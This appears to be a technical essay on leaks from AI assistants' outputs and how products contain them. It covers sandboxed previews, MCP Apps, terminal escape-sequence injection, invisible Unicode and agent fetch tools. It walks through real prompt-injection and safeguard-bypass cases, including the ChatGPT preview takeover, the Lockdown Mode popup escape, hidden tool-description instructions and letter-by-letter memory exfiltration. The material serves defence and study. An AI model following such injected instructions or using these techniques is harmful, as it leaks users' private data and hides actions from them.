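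None of the researchers reported an attacker using these methods against Copilot. Microsoft told Aim that EchoLeak had affected no customers, and Cato knew of no attacks with ReLeak when it published, but Taler doesn't say whether anyone looked for attacks with SearchLeak. Microsoft's statement about EchoLeak is the strongest evidence, because the relayed requests came from Microsoft's servers and Microsoft could in principle search its records for them. A customer would have had much less evidence, because the leak would appear in its network logs as an employee's browser loading a picture from Teams or Bing, which is routine in any office that uses Microsoft's software.

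## Sandboxes for interfaces that a model writes

Chat assistants now write whole web pages as well as formatted text. The office worker might ask for a page that lists the invoices in the twelve emails, with buttons to sort them and a slider that shows the effect of paying late. The model writes the HTML, styles and scripts, and the product displays the page beside the conversation. Output encoding would show the worker the source code instead, and a sanitiser would remove the scripts that make the buttons work. Since the product has to run code that an attacker may have influenced, it uses a sandbox to limit the harm the code can do.

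### What each layer of isolation withholds

A web page can embed another page in a frame. A careful product gives the frame a separate origin, a sandbox and a Content Security Policy (CSP), which restrict different things. The mail site might embed the invoice page like this:

```
<iframe sandbox="allow-scripts"
  src="https://preview.example/invoices"></iframe>
```

Because `preview.example` is a different origin, the same-origin policy stops the invoice page's scripts from reading the mail site's page, cookies or stored data.

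The `sandbox` attribute removes further abilities. If it is empty, the framed page can't run scripts, submit forms, open windows or send the whole tab to another address. The developer can restore abilities one at a time, and here restores only scripts. The browser also gives a sandboxed page its own origin, which matches no other, unless the developer adds `allow-same-origin`.

That confusingly named permission lets the page keep the origin of its real address, which is harmless if the address is on `preview.example`. If the mail site served the page from its own address and also allowed scripts, a script in the frame could access the page around it and remove the sandbox.

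The CSP on the framed page controls its network requests. It can block requests to every outside address and still allow inline scripts with `unsafe-inline`. That keyword weakens policies on ordinary websites, but here the product trusts none of the scripts, so the browser doesn't need to distinguish trusted scripts from injected ones.

| Layer | What the code in the frame loses | What it can still do |
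|---|---|---|
| Separate origin | Access to the mail site's page, cookies and storage | Contact other servers, open windows, send messages to the mail page |
| Sandbox that allows only scripts | Forms, new windows, control of the whole tab | Request images and other files, send messages to the mail page |
| CSP that forbids outside addresses | Images, files and connections from other servers | Send its own frame to another address, send messages to the mail page, deceive the user |

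A script that navigates its own frame to a new address can put data in that address. The mail site can limit this by listing permitted frame addresses under `frame-src` in its own policy.

The invoice page contains the reference number FT4821 because the worker asked for it, so a hostile script in the page can read the number without escaping the frame. The separate origin protects the rest of the mailbox. Whether the script can send the number out of the frame depends on the other two layers.

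INCIBE's *CVE-2025-50733* (2025) describes a flaw in the HTML preview of NextChat, an open-source chat interface. The record lists the causes as a frame that allowed scripts and a lack of proper sanitisation. But a preview of an interactive page has to allow scripts, and a sanitiser that removed them would stop the page from working. It is more useful to ask which origin the scripts run in and what they can contact.

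### ChatGPT's preview: a message to the main page

In February 2026 OpenAI added a preview to ChatGPT that turns a block of HTML code into a working page. The preview ran the page in a restricted frame on a separate web address. In October the security company Parameter found a way from that frame into the account of anyone who opened a shared conversation. *Do the Math* (Goyal, 2026) explains how the attack combined features that were harmless on their own.

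The isolation prevented code in the preview from reading the ChatGPT page around it. But browsers let pages from different origins exchange messages through a function called `postMessage`, which many sites need for features such as embedded maps and payment forms. The browser delivers the message, and the receiving page has to check who sent it.

If a conversation contained an interactive graph, ChatGPT's main page loaded MathLive, a library for displaying and typing mathematics. MathLive listened for messages that change the layout of its on-screen keyboard, and accepted them from any sender. That might never matter on a page without hostile frames, but OpenAI's preview let code from strangers send messages to MathLive.

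A keyboard layout could contain HTML, which MathLive assigned to `innerHTML` in the main page. MathLive first passed the HTML through a helper called `createHTML`, which only marked the string as trusted, though Goyal's team initially thought it might be a sanitiser. Trusted Types uses the same name for the function that is supposed to make HTML safe. A policy in Edge's Copilot panel had also returned every string unchanged.

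The researchers could now put markup into the main page, but script elements inserted through `innerHTML` don't run. They instead inserted a frame with its content written directly in the markup. A browser gives such a frame the origin of the containing page unless a `sandbox` attribute prevents this. MathLive had not added one, so any script in the frame would run with the `chatgpt.com` origin.

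ChatGPT's CSP still blocked inline scripts and allowed script files from only a handful of domains. One of these was YouTube, which had a JSONP endpoint. The endpoint returned an error message because the function name in the researchers' request was invalid, but it copied that name into the start of the response. The browser ran the response because it came from YouTube.

The nonces and `strict-dynamic` that Google's own researchers proposed in 2016 would have blocked this script, because the browser would have ignored the entry for YouTube.

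The researchers' script could list the victim's conversations, read one that the victim had never shared, and send its contents to an outside server. It could also do anything else on the site that the victim could do.

The researchers needed several attempts to fit all this into one link. An early version sent the messages from their own ChatGPT app, which a victim would first have had to connect or use. They then tried an HTML attachment, but the shared copy of the conversation lost the graph, without which the main page never loaded MathLive. Finally they put a graph and a preview in the same ordinary conversation. In the most reliable version, the victim opened the link and clicked "Preview" once. In another, the preview opened by itself, which worked three times in a separate account.

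OpenAI classed the report as P1, a high priority, and fixed the flaw on 26 October, two days after the researchers reported it (O’Shei, 2026, *ChatGPT share links bypassed sandboxes through math embeds*). OpenAI paid them $5,000, which Willison (2026, *How We Took Over ChatGPT Accounts*) thought "a bit cheap" for such a serious flaw.

OpenAI had restricted the code inside the frame, but the frame's safety also depended on every script outside it that listened for messages. A developer can list those listeners and check that each one verifies the sender, but has to repeat the check whenever a library changes. Few developers would expect a graph to install a message listener for a keyboard.

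### Lockdown Mode and the permitted popup

Lockdown Mode is an optional setting for ChatGPT users who want stronger protection against leaks than the default. OpenAI first offered it on enterprise plans and extended it to personal accounts in June 2026, according to *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. It is meant to stop the last step of an attack, in which private data leaves the conversation, even if the prompt injection succeeds.

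OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* lists what users give up when they turn the feature on. ChatGPT reads only stored copies of web pages and may not display images in ordinary replies. It can't download files for analysis, and deep research and agent modes are off. Users can't allow code from Canvas, ChatGPT's editing panel, to access the network. Lockdown Mode doesn't switch off every connected app, and on company accounts administrators decide which ones remain available. The restrictions don't apply to Codex, OpenAI's coding agent.

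Willison (2026) pointed out that offering such a mode implies that ChatGPT's ordinary settings don't robustly protect against a determined attacker. Even with the mode on, OpenAI doesn't promise complete protection and warns of "unforeseen combinations of capabilities". The security company Check Point found one such combination in the HTML preview, which isn't on the help page's list of restricted features.

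The preview's two nested frames intercepted requests to outside servers and asked the user to approve them. New windows needed separate treatment, because CSP doesn't control them. Duggan (2026), in *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup*, explains that ChatGPT replaced `window.open`, the function that opens a window, with a version that asked for approval. But every frame has its own copy of that function, so a previewed page could create a frame inside itself and use that frame's copy, which ChatGPT had not replaced.

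The browser could still have blocked the window, but OpenAI had given the frame two permissions, `allow-popups` and `allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox`. The first let the page open windows, and the second freed those windows from the sandbox's restrictions. OpenAI's reasons aren't public. It may have wanted links in previewed pages to work, since many websites break if they open inside a sandbox.

A new window can load an address that contains private data, so the popup let an attacker make the outgoing request that Lockdown Mode was meant to prevent. Browsers normally open a window only after a click, but the older ChatGPT desktop app, ChatGPT Classic, didn't require one. Check Point showed that a malicious custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT with instructions written by a third party, could send the whole chat to an outside server while the user was simply talking to it.

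In the desktop app, the window had ChatGPT's icon and a title the attacker chose, so a fake update notice looked like part of the program. Check Point could also sign the user out and show a fake login page in the app's main window.

An attacker could deliver the hostile page through a prompt, a custom GPT or a shared chat. Lockdown Mode doesn't restrict shared conversations, and someone who opened one in a browser could receive a malicious download without having an account.

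On 18 September OpenAI told Check Point that it had removed both permissions from the outer frame. A frame can't have permissions that the frame around it lacks, so the removal applied to every frame a page might create. Check Point retested the attack, and it no longer worked. Check Point published its findings on 5 November and reported no real attacks.

Like the filters of the early web, OpenAI's original approach tried to intercept each route by which a page might open a window, and it missed one. Removing the permission makes the browser itself block new windows, whichever route the page uses. The drawback is probably that links in previews no longer open in new windows.

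Check Point told The Hacker News (*Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction*, 2026) that its flaw and Parameter's were different vulnerabilities in the same component. The September fix didn't hinder Parameter's attack in October because that attack opened no windows. Checking messages in the main page wouldn't have stopped Check Point's popup, so a preview needs both the September fix and message checks.

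### MCP Apps and OpenAI's Apps SDK

An assistant can also display interfaces that outside companies supply, so the model doesn't have to write them. An accounting service might provide an invoice table, for example. OpenAI's Apps SDK is a toolkit for building applications with such interfaces inside ChatGPT. It uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting assistants to outside tools and data.

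In November 2025, maintainers of the protocol at OpenAI and Anthropic and the creators of MCP-UI, an earlier community project, proposed a common standard called MCP Apps (Model Context Protocol, 2025). *SEP-1865* (Salomon, Yosef and colleagues, 2025) sets out the rules, which have been stable since January 2026. The outside company's server supplies the page, and the chat product, called the host, displays it in a frame. The model decides when to call the tool that the page belongs to.

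The host can inspect the page before anyone uses it, because a developer wrote it in advance and the data for each conversation arrives separately. This is an advantage over ChatGPT's preview, where the model writes the code during the conversation.

If the host is a web page, it must place an intermediate page, the sandbox proxy, between itself and the app. The proxy's sandbox must allow scripts and include `allow-same-origin`. This combination is safe because the proxy must have a different origin from the host. The proxy loads the app with a CSP and passes messages between the app and the host.

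Apps also need protection from one another, because two apps with the same origin could read each other's stored data. The specification lets an app request its own origin, in a format set by each host. According to Daily AI News' *MCP App CSP Explained*, a guide for developers, ChatGPT puts each app on its own subdomain of `web-sandbox.oaiusercontent.com`, while Claude computes the app's address from its server's URL.

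If an app declares no domains, the host must apply a strict default policy. The page can run the scripts it contains, because the policy includes `unsafe-inline`, and it can show images embedded in it as `data:` URLs. It can't load anything from an outside server or connect to one. The policy also permits files from the page's own origin, but this adds almost nothing because, as Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS* explains, the frame has no server of its own behind it. Developers therefore need to declare a domain even to load their own script files.

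An app with this policy can still send data to the company that made it by asking the host to call tools on that company's server. The host can pass on whatever the app puts in the request. It may block the call or ask the user first, but the specification doesn't require either. The strict default therefore keeps data from third parties, but the worker has to trust the accounting service with everything its app receives.

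Apps and hosts communicate through `postMessage`, the function Parameter exploited. The proxy gives them a channel for this, but an app can also send a message directly to the outermost page, where any listener that doesn't validate messages will accept it. An early version of Parameter's attack worked this way, with a ChatGPT app sending the message. A host that follows the specification exactly therefore still has to check the other scripts on its page.

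The specification's sample code for developers who don't use the official library has a related weakness. It accepts any reply that carries the expected number, without checking who sent it. The sample runs inside the app's frame, so a forged message would mislead the app but wouldn't give the attacker access to the chat product. But developers copy sample code, and the check would have been easy to include.

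An app can also request that the host draw no border around it. Without a border, the app looks like part of the assistant's own answer, so an attacker could use it to show a false security notice. The host can protect users by always marking where an app begins and ends, even when the app requests no border.

### Who declares the permitted domains

An app must declare any outside domains it needs in four lists, which cover connections opened by scripts, resources such as images and fonts, embedded frames, and the base address for relative links. The server supplies the lists and the host turns them into a CSP. The host may make the policy stricter but must not permit undeclared domains. Salomon and colleagues also recommend that hosts log these policies for security review.

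The company whose code needs restricting therefore writes its own list of permissions. On the web, a site's owner writes the list to protect the site from injected text, so the owner benefits from keeping it short. A malicious app maker could list a server it controls, and the host would then let the app leak data to that server. The added danger is limited, since the maker can already receive data through its tools. The list is mainly useful for containing mistakes in honest apps and for letting the host see which other companies may receive data.

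Whether this repeats the web's allowlist problem depends on what the list is meant to prevent. In the 2016 study of CSP, the main danger was that a trusted domain would let an attacker run a script with the whole site's authority. An MCP app has no authority over the chat product, so an extra script in its frame gains no access to the user's conversations. Parameter's use of YouTube was different because its new frame had ChatGPT's own origin.

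Scripts can still harm the app itself. Suppose the accounting service's page displays a supplier's name with `innerHTML`. A supplier could put an event handler in its name, and the default policy would let the handler run because it allows inline code. The supplier's code could then call any tool the app can call, perhaps one that approves a payment. App developers need the ordinary defences against XSS inside the frame, since neither the frame nor the default policy provides them.

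Data can leak from these apps in almost the same way as before. An app that declared the Teams and Bing relay domains could send data through those relays. Narrow permissions are also harder to write, because a single resource list covers images, scripts, styles, fonts and media. A developer who needs one font from a domain must also permit images from it, unless the host tightens the policy.

The lists can include wildcards. The official Model Context Protocol reference, *Interface McpUiResourceCsp*, gives as examples `https://*.cloudflare.com` and jsDelivr, a public service that delivers code packages. Anyone can publish a package there. An app that loads a script from such a service can also change its behaviour after the host has inspected its page.

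A host could also review a short list of domains and then enforce a longer one. A server can declare domains when the host connects and again when the host loads the page, and the later declaration takes precedence. The second declaration helps apps whose needs vary, but a careful host would refuse any domain missing from the list it reviewed. The specification permits this because refusing domains only makes the policy stricter.

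MCP Apps still starts from a better position than most websites did. Site owners had to add a policy to old pages that already loaded files from many places, and nothing broke if they left it out. An MCP app starts with no network access, so if its developer forgets to list a domain the app needs, the app visibly fails. Each app also has its own list of allowed domains, which should be much shorter than a list for a whole chat product, and a leak exposes only what that app could reach.

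The visible failure also puts pressure on developers to loosen their policies. Daily AI News wrote its guide for people whose apps show up blank, and the quickest fix is to declare more domains. Website developers loosened their policies for the same reason. MCP hosts can resist this more easily than browser makers could, because a company that runs a directory of apps can refuse a broad wildcard before any user sees the app. The safety of the lists will depend on how many hosts do this.

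### Fixed components instead of HTML

A product can avoid running untrusted code by not accepting a page from the model. In December 2025 Google published A2UI, an open format in which an agent describes an interface as data. The host's own developers write a catalogue of components, such as text, buttons and date pickers. The model chooses components from the catalogue and supplies their values, and the host draws them.

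Suppose the mail site's catalogue includes a card for invoices. In a simplified version of such a format, the model might write:

```
{ "component": "InvoiceCard",
  "sender": "Earl's <b>Tea</b>",
  "due": "2026-12-11",
  "email": 7 }
```

The mail site's program reads this as data and handles each part separately.

| Part | What the program does | What the worker sees |
|---|---|---|
| Component | Looks up the name in the catalogue and refuses an unknown one | A card in the mail site's usual design |
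| Sender | Inserts the value as plain text | `Earl's <b>Tea</b>`, exactly as written |
| Due date | Checks that the value is a date | 11 December 2026 |
| Email | Checks that the worker can open message 7 and builds the link itself | A button that opens the message |

The developer writes the card's markup in advance and the model fills in the values, much as in Google's strict templates. The program can distinguish structure from values, even if the model was following a hostile email when it wrote the values. No value can become a script or an event handler, so the card doesn't need a sandbox.

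The separation isn't quite as complete as in a template, because the model also chooses which components appear and in what order. A hostile email could make it choose the wrong ones. If the sender's name contained a quotation mark and the model copied it without escaping it, the rest of the name might add a new field to the data. In either case the screen could contain only components from the catalogue, so the mail site's developers can go through the catalogue and work out the worst screen an attacker could produce, which they couldn't do for a page of free-form HTML.

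This makes the choice of components a security decision. A password field would let the stranger build a false login form in the mail site's design. An image component that accepted any address would again let data leak through image requests. A text component that accepted Markdown would need the same protection as any other chat reply. Even a plain text field could display the stranger's false phone number for the bank.

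A2UI also separates the data on a screen from the components that display it, so the mail program could copy the sender and due date directly from the email and let the model supply only the layout. The model could then not alter those values, but it could still leave out an invoice or put a misleading heading above one.

The catalogue limits the worker to what its components can express. A sorted list of invoice cards is easy, but the slider that shows the effect of paying late is impossible unless the mail site's developers have built a component for it. An HTML preview could have had the slider working in seconds. Adding a component for every such request would mean writing and reviewing a great deal of code. A general component that ran formulas written as text would be more flexible, but if it ran them as ordinary code, it would bring back the problem that AngularJS's expressions caused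 on pages with a CSP.

MCP Apps instead began with HTML, which lets developers reuse ordinary web pages, though the specification leaves room for other formats. A mail assistant could reasonably use both approaches. Buttons that send a message or approve a payment belong in fixed components, where the program can check each value before it acts. The late-payment slider needs only a few amounts and dates, so the program could give those to a sandboxed frame with no network access and leave out the reference numbers.

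## Command-line agents: encoding output for a terminal

Many coding agents, including Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex CLI, run in a terminal, the text window where programmers type commands. A terminal doesn't parse HTML, so an image tag in a model's reply appears as ordinary text and loads nothing. But it treats some characters as commands, and it has no same-origin policy or Content Security Policy to limit what they do. The agent's own program therefore has to make the text safe before printing it.

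### How a terminal reads text

Modern terminals imitate machines such as Digital Equipment Corporation's VT100, as the security researcher David Leadbeater explains in a paper on dgl.cx. A program sends the terminal a single stream of characters, most of which appear on the screen. The exceptions are control characters, such as newline, tab and backspace. One of them, escape (character 27), begins a longer command called a control sequence.

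Suppose a program prints this line, in which ␛ stands for the escape character:

```
I <3 ␛[31mtea␛[0m
```

The terminal draws the heart as typed, because an angle bracket has no special meaning to a terminal. It stops drawing at the escape character and starts reading a command. The square bracket means numbers may follow, and the letter `m` ends the command and marks it as a change of style. Style 31 is red, so "tea" appears in red. The second sequence restores the normal style.

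The ECMA-48 standard defines many of the common sequences, according to Chromium's documentation for Google's terminal. The original ANSI standard didn't specify what to do with a malformed sequence, so Leadbeater urges terminal makers to copy the VT100's behaviour exactly. He compares this to the HTML standard's rules for invalid input.

Programs need these sequences to draw anything more elaborate than plain lines. GitHub's *From pixels to characters*, about the animated banner in its Copilot command-line agent, explains that a terminal has no canvas, so the program repaints every frame by moving the cursor and writing over what was there. An attacker whose text reaches the terminal can use the same features:

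- Text in the same colour as the background is invisible, and a backspace lets later characters replace earlier ones.
- Cursor movements can overwrite lines already on the screen, or clear the screen completely.
- A link can display one address and lead to another.
- A sequence called OSC 52 puts text on the user's clipboard. It has a good use, since it lets people copy from a remote machine (jvns.ca's *Standards for ANSI escape codes* (2025)), but an attacker can use it to plant a command that the user later pastes.

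In 2022 and 2023, Leadbeater found ten flaws in terminals themselves that could let an attacker run code. In several cases, the terminal responded to a query by entering the attacker's text as if the user had typed it. Terminal makers have fixed most of these flaws, but they are unlikely to remove support for colours and cursor movement, so hidden and overwritten text will remain possible.

### Models that write control characters

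In late 2024 Leon Derczynski reported that many models can write the escape character itself. In *Terminal DiLLMa*, published on Embrace The Red, Rehberger describes testing whether a stranger's text could make a model do so. He wrote a small command-line program that sent a file or web page to OpenAI's GPT-4o and printed the reply unchanged. When he asked for a summary of a hostile page, the reply changed the text colour, moved the cursor, cleared the screen and beeped. He also found that models could read control characters, so an attacker could put a sequence in the page and ask the model to repeat it.

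The test showed that private data could leave through a terminal much as it leaves through a chat window. In the terminal of Microsoft's VS Code editor, the reply could contain a link with data from the conversation in its address, though the editor asked for confirmation before opening the link. The program was Rehberger's own demonstration, so the test didn't prove that any product had the flaw.

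Apple's Terminal could leak data without a click. One control sequence gives the current folder as an address, and Terminal looked up the host name in that address, apparently to check whether the folder was on the same machine. If the office worker's mail assistant ran in Terminal, the stranger could ask it to print this sequence with the reference number FT4821 in front of a domain name the stranger controlled. The lookup would then send the number to the stranger's name server, much as a browser's name lookups can.

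Developers can now test for this behaviour with garak, an open-source scanner for language models. It has probes that prompt a model to produce control sequences, either as raw characters or spelled out.

### Hidden text in tool descriptions

Each tool that a coding agent connects to through the Model Context Protocol (MCP) supplies a description for the model to read. In April 2025, the security company Trail of Bits tested Claude Code version 0.2.76 and found that it displayed tool descriptions and results without filtering out control sequences (*Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP*, 2025).

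The researchers built a tool that returned a dull summary of a user's computers. It included a claim, in white text, that the Windows machine had to download Python packages from a particular server. The developer couldn't see this sentence, but the model read it and later recommended the server. This version works only on a white terminal background, and many programmers prefer a dark one. Two other versions work with any colours. In one, a fake report of a clean security scan overwrote the hostile instruction on the screen. In the other, the tool's output included an instruction to add a back door to the developer's software, then cleared the screen and printed blank lines so that the window seemed to have scrolled.

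Cross-site scripting runs the attacker's text as code, whereas this terminal attack only hides text from the developer, the one person who might have objected to it. Hiding text matters because coding agents rely heavily on developers to read what is on the screen and approve it.

Trail of Bits recommended replacing every escape character with a harmless placeholder because, it said, all sequences in modern terminals begin with one. According to Leadbeater, however, a few terminals, including Kitty and WezTerm, also accept an older set of control characters, numbered 128 to 159, one of which can start a sequence in place of an escape and a square bracket. Replacing only the escape character also leaves backspaces in the text. In July 2025, Trail of Bits released a wrapper for MCP tools that has an option to clean control characters from their text (Trail of Bits' *We built the security layer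 MCP always needed* (2025)).

### Making control characters visible

A more complete fix is to print every control character in a visible notation. In caret notation, the program writes a caret followed by the character 64 places higher in the ASCII table. Escape is number 27 and the left square bracket is number 91, so escape becomes `^[`. Backspace, number 8, becomes `^H`.

| Treatment | What the program sends | What the developer sees |
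|---|---|---|
| HTML encoding | `I &lt;3 ␛[31mtea␛[0m` | `I &lt;3 tea`, with "tea" still in red |
| Removing whole sequences | `I <3 tea` | `I <3 tea`, with no sign that anything is missing |
| Caret notation | `I <3 ^[[31mtea^[[0m` | Exactly what the program sent |

HTML encoding damages the heart and leaves the sequence working, because it is meant for HTML rather than a terminal. Removing sequences gives the cleanest result, but the program has to recognise every kind. Removing one sequence from the middle of another can also join the remaining pieces into a new one, and any filter that deletes text in a single pass has this weakness.

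Caret notation avoids both problems because it encodes each character separately. An encoded escape character can't start a command, whatever follows it. Unfinished replies, which caused leaks in GitLab's and Microsoft's chat windows, are therefore as easy to encode as finished ones.

Unicode has only 65 control characters, and a program that keeps newline and tab has to encode the other 63. Encoding all 63 is safer than picking out the dangerous ones. A logging library on Searchfox, a site for browsing source code, encodes the range from 128 to 159 but only five of the other 33 control characters. It omits the carriage return, which moves the cursor to the start of the line, where later text can overwrite what is already there.

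Developers lose very little by encoding a model's reply this way, because the model writes its formatting in Markdown and the agent's program can turn `**tea**` into bold with a control sequence. The program must encode the model's text before adding its own sequences, since encoding the finished screen would turn those sequences into visible carets and brackets. Google's security types could also help by marking which strings the program has already encoded.

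Output from other programs is harder to handle, because a testing tool might print its failures in red and the developer would want to keep the colour. OpenAI's Codex CLI contains a helper that parses control sequences into styled text objects, which the interface then draws (OpenAI's *oai-codex-ansi-escape* (2025)). These objects can represent colour but not cursor movements or clipboard writes, so the helper works much like a parser-based HTML sanitiser.

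Even the simple fix can be awkward to add to a working product. Hoxha's *Merge pull request #176 from charmbracelet/escape-sequences* added visible encoding to Crush, a coding agent, with tests in which a red string becomes visible notation and ordinary Japanese text stays the same. Hoxha's *Merge pull request #192 from charmbracelet/revert-176-escape-sequences* then undid the change, though perhaps not because of the encoding, since the same change had altered how Crush read files. A separate version, Bagabas's *fix(tui): escape control characters in tool call content*, first converts Windows line endings, because they contain a carriage return that would otherwise appear as a stray `^M` at the end of every line of a Windows file.

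### The same flaw in one display after another

These flaws predate coding agents. *Weaponizing Plain Text* (STÖK, 2023) lists a 2010 advisory about ten web servers, including Nginx, that wrote visitors' control sequences into their logs, where the sequences could affect the terminal of an administrator reading them. In 2022 Eviatar Gerzi reported a similar flaw in `kubectl`, the command-line tool for the Kubernetes server software. According to Leadbeater, the Kubernetes project didn't consider the flaw serious, and it stayed open until Leadbeater wrote the fix. MITRE has a general entry for the weakness, with "ANSI injection" as an alternative name.

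Agents display text in many places, and their developers have been finding the flaw in each place separately. In March 2026 OpenClaw, an open-source agent, fixed it in approval prompts and permission logs. A tool's title could carry control sequences into both, so a hostile tool could forge part of the question the user was answering (GitHub Advisory Database's *OpenClaw has ACP CLI approval prompt ANSI escape sequence injection* (2026)). OpenClaw already removed some control sequences, but not all of those that set colours and move the cursor. The fix removes all of them and cleans each title at its source. The advisory rates the flaw as only moderate, perhaps because an attacker still needs the user to approve something.

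Anthropic made a similar repair to Claude Code that July, according to the release notes. It stopped control characters in the output of background agents from reaching the terminal. The flaw was in the agent view, a screen that lists several agents at once. The note mentions only this view, so Anthropic had probably already protected the main conversation.

In August it fixed the dialog that asks a developer to approve a command. *Claude Code v2.1.223 Major Updates* (Ishikawa, 2026) reports that tabs or invisible Unicode characters could hide part of the command. A tab is one of the two control characters that an encoder normally keeps, and it is harmless in a reply, but enough tabs in an approval dialog can presumably push the rest of a command out of sight. The dialog therefore needs stricter rules than the conversation, although both appear in the same terminal.

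Since 30 October, one of Claude Code's lists of blocked actions has also prevented developers from approving an action they can't read in full, even if only because the window is too short (Anthropic, 2026). This rule doesn't depend on identifying the trick that hid the text. The same release fixed a bug where setting `FORCE_HYPERLINK` to "false" turned terminal links on.

Add-ons can reintroduce the flaw. Claude HUD, a separate add-on for Claude Code, displays the current folder and code branch as links. It put their names into the link's control sequence without encoding them, so a specially named folder could end the link early and start another command (VulnCheck's *Claude HUD 0.0.12 Terminal Injection via OSC 8 Hyperlinks*). Encoding the finished line would have broken the link by also encoding its intended control sequence, so each value needed encoding for its place inside the sequence.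 Google's templates solve this problem for HTML, and terminal programs could use a similar tool.

Output encoding has carried over to terminals almost unchanged, because developers know the output is going to a terminal and can list the characters that are special there. But they have been slower to notice how many prompts, logs and status lines need encoding.

### Invisible Unicode characters

Some Unicode characters are invisible but aren't control characters, so the terminal's encoder leaves them unchanged. The best known in attacks on models are the tag characters, which are invisible copies of the ASCII characters. Each copy's number is 917,504 higher than the original's, so the letter "t" is number 116 and its invisible copy is number 917,620. If a message contains `I <3` followed by the invisible copies of "tea", a person sees only `I <3`, but a model may also read "tea".

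According to *Trust No AI*, Riley Goodside discovered that models interpret these characters, and researchers soon found that models can also write them. In February 2024 Rehberger used both abilities in an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot. An email made the assistant find sensitive information in the user's mailbox and hide it in a link as invisible characters. The link would have looked ordinary to a user who inspected it, but clicking it would have sent the hidden data to the attacker's server. Microsoft fixed the flaw that July.

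Tag characters still work against newer products. *The Invisible Payload* (Vaughan, 2026) reports on a July 2026 paper by Rashidi about MCP tool descriptions. A hostile server can write instructions in tag characters, which the model receives in full but no mainstream terminal, chat window or code editor displays. A developer will miss these instructions even when reading the description carefully before approving the tool.

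Visible notation could, in principle, work here too. A program could print the hidden word as `<U+E0074><U+E0065><U+E0061>`, using each character's hexadecimal number. But it is hard to decide which characters to encode, because some invisible characters have legitimate uses. The flags of Scotland and Wales contain tag characters, an invisible joiner holds family emoji together, and Persian spelling uses a similar character between letters. The Unix command `cat -v` encodes everything outside ASCII, which removes the need to choose but makes Japanese unreadable. There is also no common reference like the VT100, because whether a person can see a character depends partly on the font.

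A program can at least set different rules for different places. In a reply, it could allow tag characters only inside a valid flag and reveal the rest. A shell command or a tool description hardly ever needs a flag, so an approval dialog could reveal every invisible character, although this would occasionally make an emoji look ugly. The program could also remove tag characters from tool descriptions and give the same cleaned copy to the model and the developer. If it cleaned only the copy on the screen, the developer would still be approving something different from what the model reads.

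## Agents that fetch pages and call tools: output as action

An agent's output can be a request to fetch a page, send an email or pay a bill, which ordinary software then carries out. The request can do harm even if nothing appears on the screen. In July 2026 a developer got personal details out of Claude's chat assistant in this way, although Anthropic had restricted which addresses the assistant could fetch.

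### Claude's memory, one letter at a time

*The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) describes two ways Claude remembers its users. A daily process condenses recent conversations into a few paragraphs about the user, and every new conversation includes those paragraphs. Claude can also search the user's whole conversation history. It therefore has access to private data whenever it reads a stranger's web page.

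Claude's tool for fetching pages was read-only, but requesting a page reveals its address to the server. Paul asked Claude to fetch an address that ended in Paul's own name, and the tool refused. It accepted an address only if at least one of these conditions held:

- The user had typed the address in a message.
- Claude's search tool had returned it.
- A page that Claude had already fetched linked to it.

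The last condition let Claude follow links as a person would. Paul built a site whose home page linked to `/a`, `/b` and so on. The page `/a` linked in turn to `/aa`, `/ab` and so on, and the server generated each new page on request. When Paul asked Claude to spell the name, it chose only from links the site provided, fetching `/a`, then `/ay`, then `/ayu`, and after ten steps the server's log contained `/ayush-paul`.

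A similar site with 36 links on each page, one for each letter and digit, could have received the mailbox's reference number, FT4821, in six requests. The 36 indexed pages that Rehberger described would also have taken six. There are about 2.2 billion possible six-character references, but the server would have needed to generate only the pages Claude visited.

Paul also had to get the model to follow injected instructions, and simple ones worked unreliably. The version that succeeded looked like a coffee shop's site behind a Cloudflare security check. It told AI assistants to identify their users by following the links letter by letter. According to Willison (2026), the site showed this text only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person inspecting the site would probably have found nothing wrong. Claude gave away the user's name, home city and employer, and its reply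 showed no sign of the leak.

Willison reports that Anthropic paid no bounty because it said it had already found the flaw. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links found in fetched pages. This blocks Paul's site, but Claude can no longer move from a contents page to a chapter unless the user or the search tool supplies the chapter's address. An attacker might still get 36 separate pages into the search results and have Claude choose among them, though this would take more preparation.

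Output encoding would not have helped, because `/ayu` contains only a slash and three letters, which a URL encoder does not change. The tool received a valid address, sent a valid request and returned the page, as its developers intended. An email tool has the same problem, since a correctly encoded message can still go to the wrong person.

### What OpenAI's link check covers

OpenAI's check on exact addresses would have stopped most of Paul's requests, because no crawler could have recorded billions of pages that did not yet exist. But Rehberger's method would still work, because it uses pages already in the index.

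Safe Url is OpenAI's check for conversation data that is about to reach a third party. OpenAI also applies it to pages and bookmarks that an agent opens in the Atlas browser, and to searches and page visits by its research agent. When the check finds such data, ChatGPT can ask the user to confirm the request, or block it and instruct the agent to try another way.

Some requests have to contain personal information to be useful. A help page from OpenAI gives the example of a car-search link that reveals that the user lives in London. The page also explains that ChatGPT asks for confirmation of every link to sites that have opted out of being catalogued by OpenAI. That is cautious, but it adds to the warnings that people may learn to click through.

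OpenAI's guarantee covers only data in the web address. An agent with an email tool could put FT4821 in the body of a message, where a check on web addresses would not detect it. Protecting such tools requires rules about what each one may do and which data it may use.

### The inherently confusable deputy

The UK's National Cyber Security Centre argued in December 2025 that prompt injection may never have a complete remedy. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, the centre's technical director for platforms research, contrasts prompt injection with older attacks.

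A parameterised query sends a database a command and its values separately. The command has a gap where a customer's name belongs, and the database never interprets what fills the gap as part of the command, so the apostrophe in "O'Brien" is harmless. XSS has comparable remedies because a browser processes text and tags differently. A language model, however, only predicts the next token (a word or part of a word) from the text so far. Developers can mark some of that text as data and train the model to treat it that way, but nothing inside the model enforces the distinction.

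David C therefore recommends treating the model as a confused deputy, a program that somebody with less authority tricks into acting for them. Developers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but a model is "inherently confusable". Developers should assume that an attacker whose text reaches the model can use all of its tools, and should limit those tools with safeguards that don't depend on a model. If an application can't tolerate the remaining risk, it may be a poor use for a model.

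David C's claim that SQL injection is now rare in websites is a little too favourable to the web. A complete remedy protects only the developers who use it, and Iqbal (2026) notes in *What It Is, Not What It Says* that SQL injection joined XSS at the top of MITRE's list in 2025.

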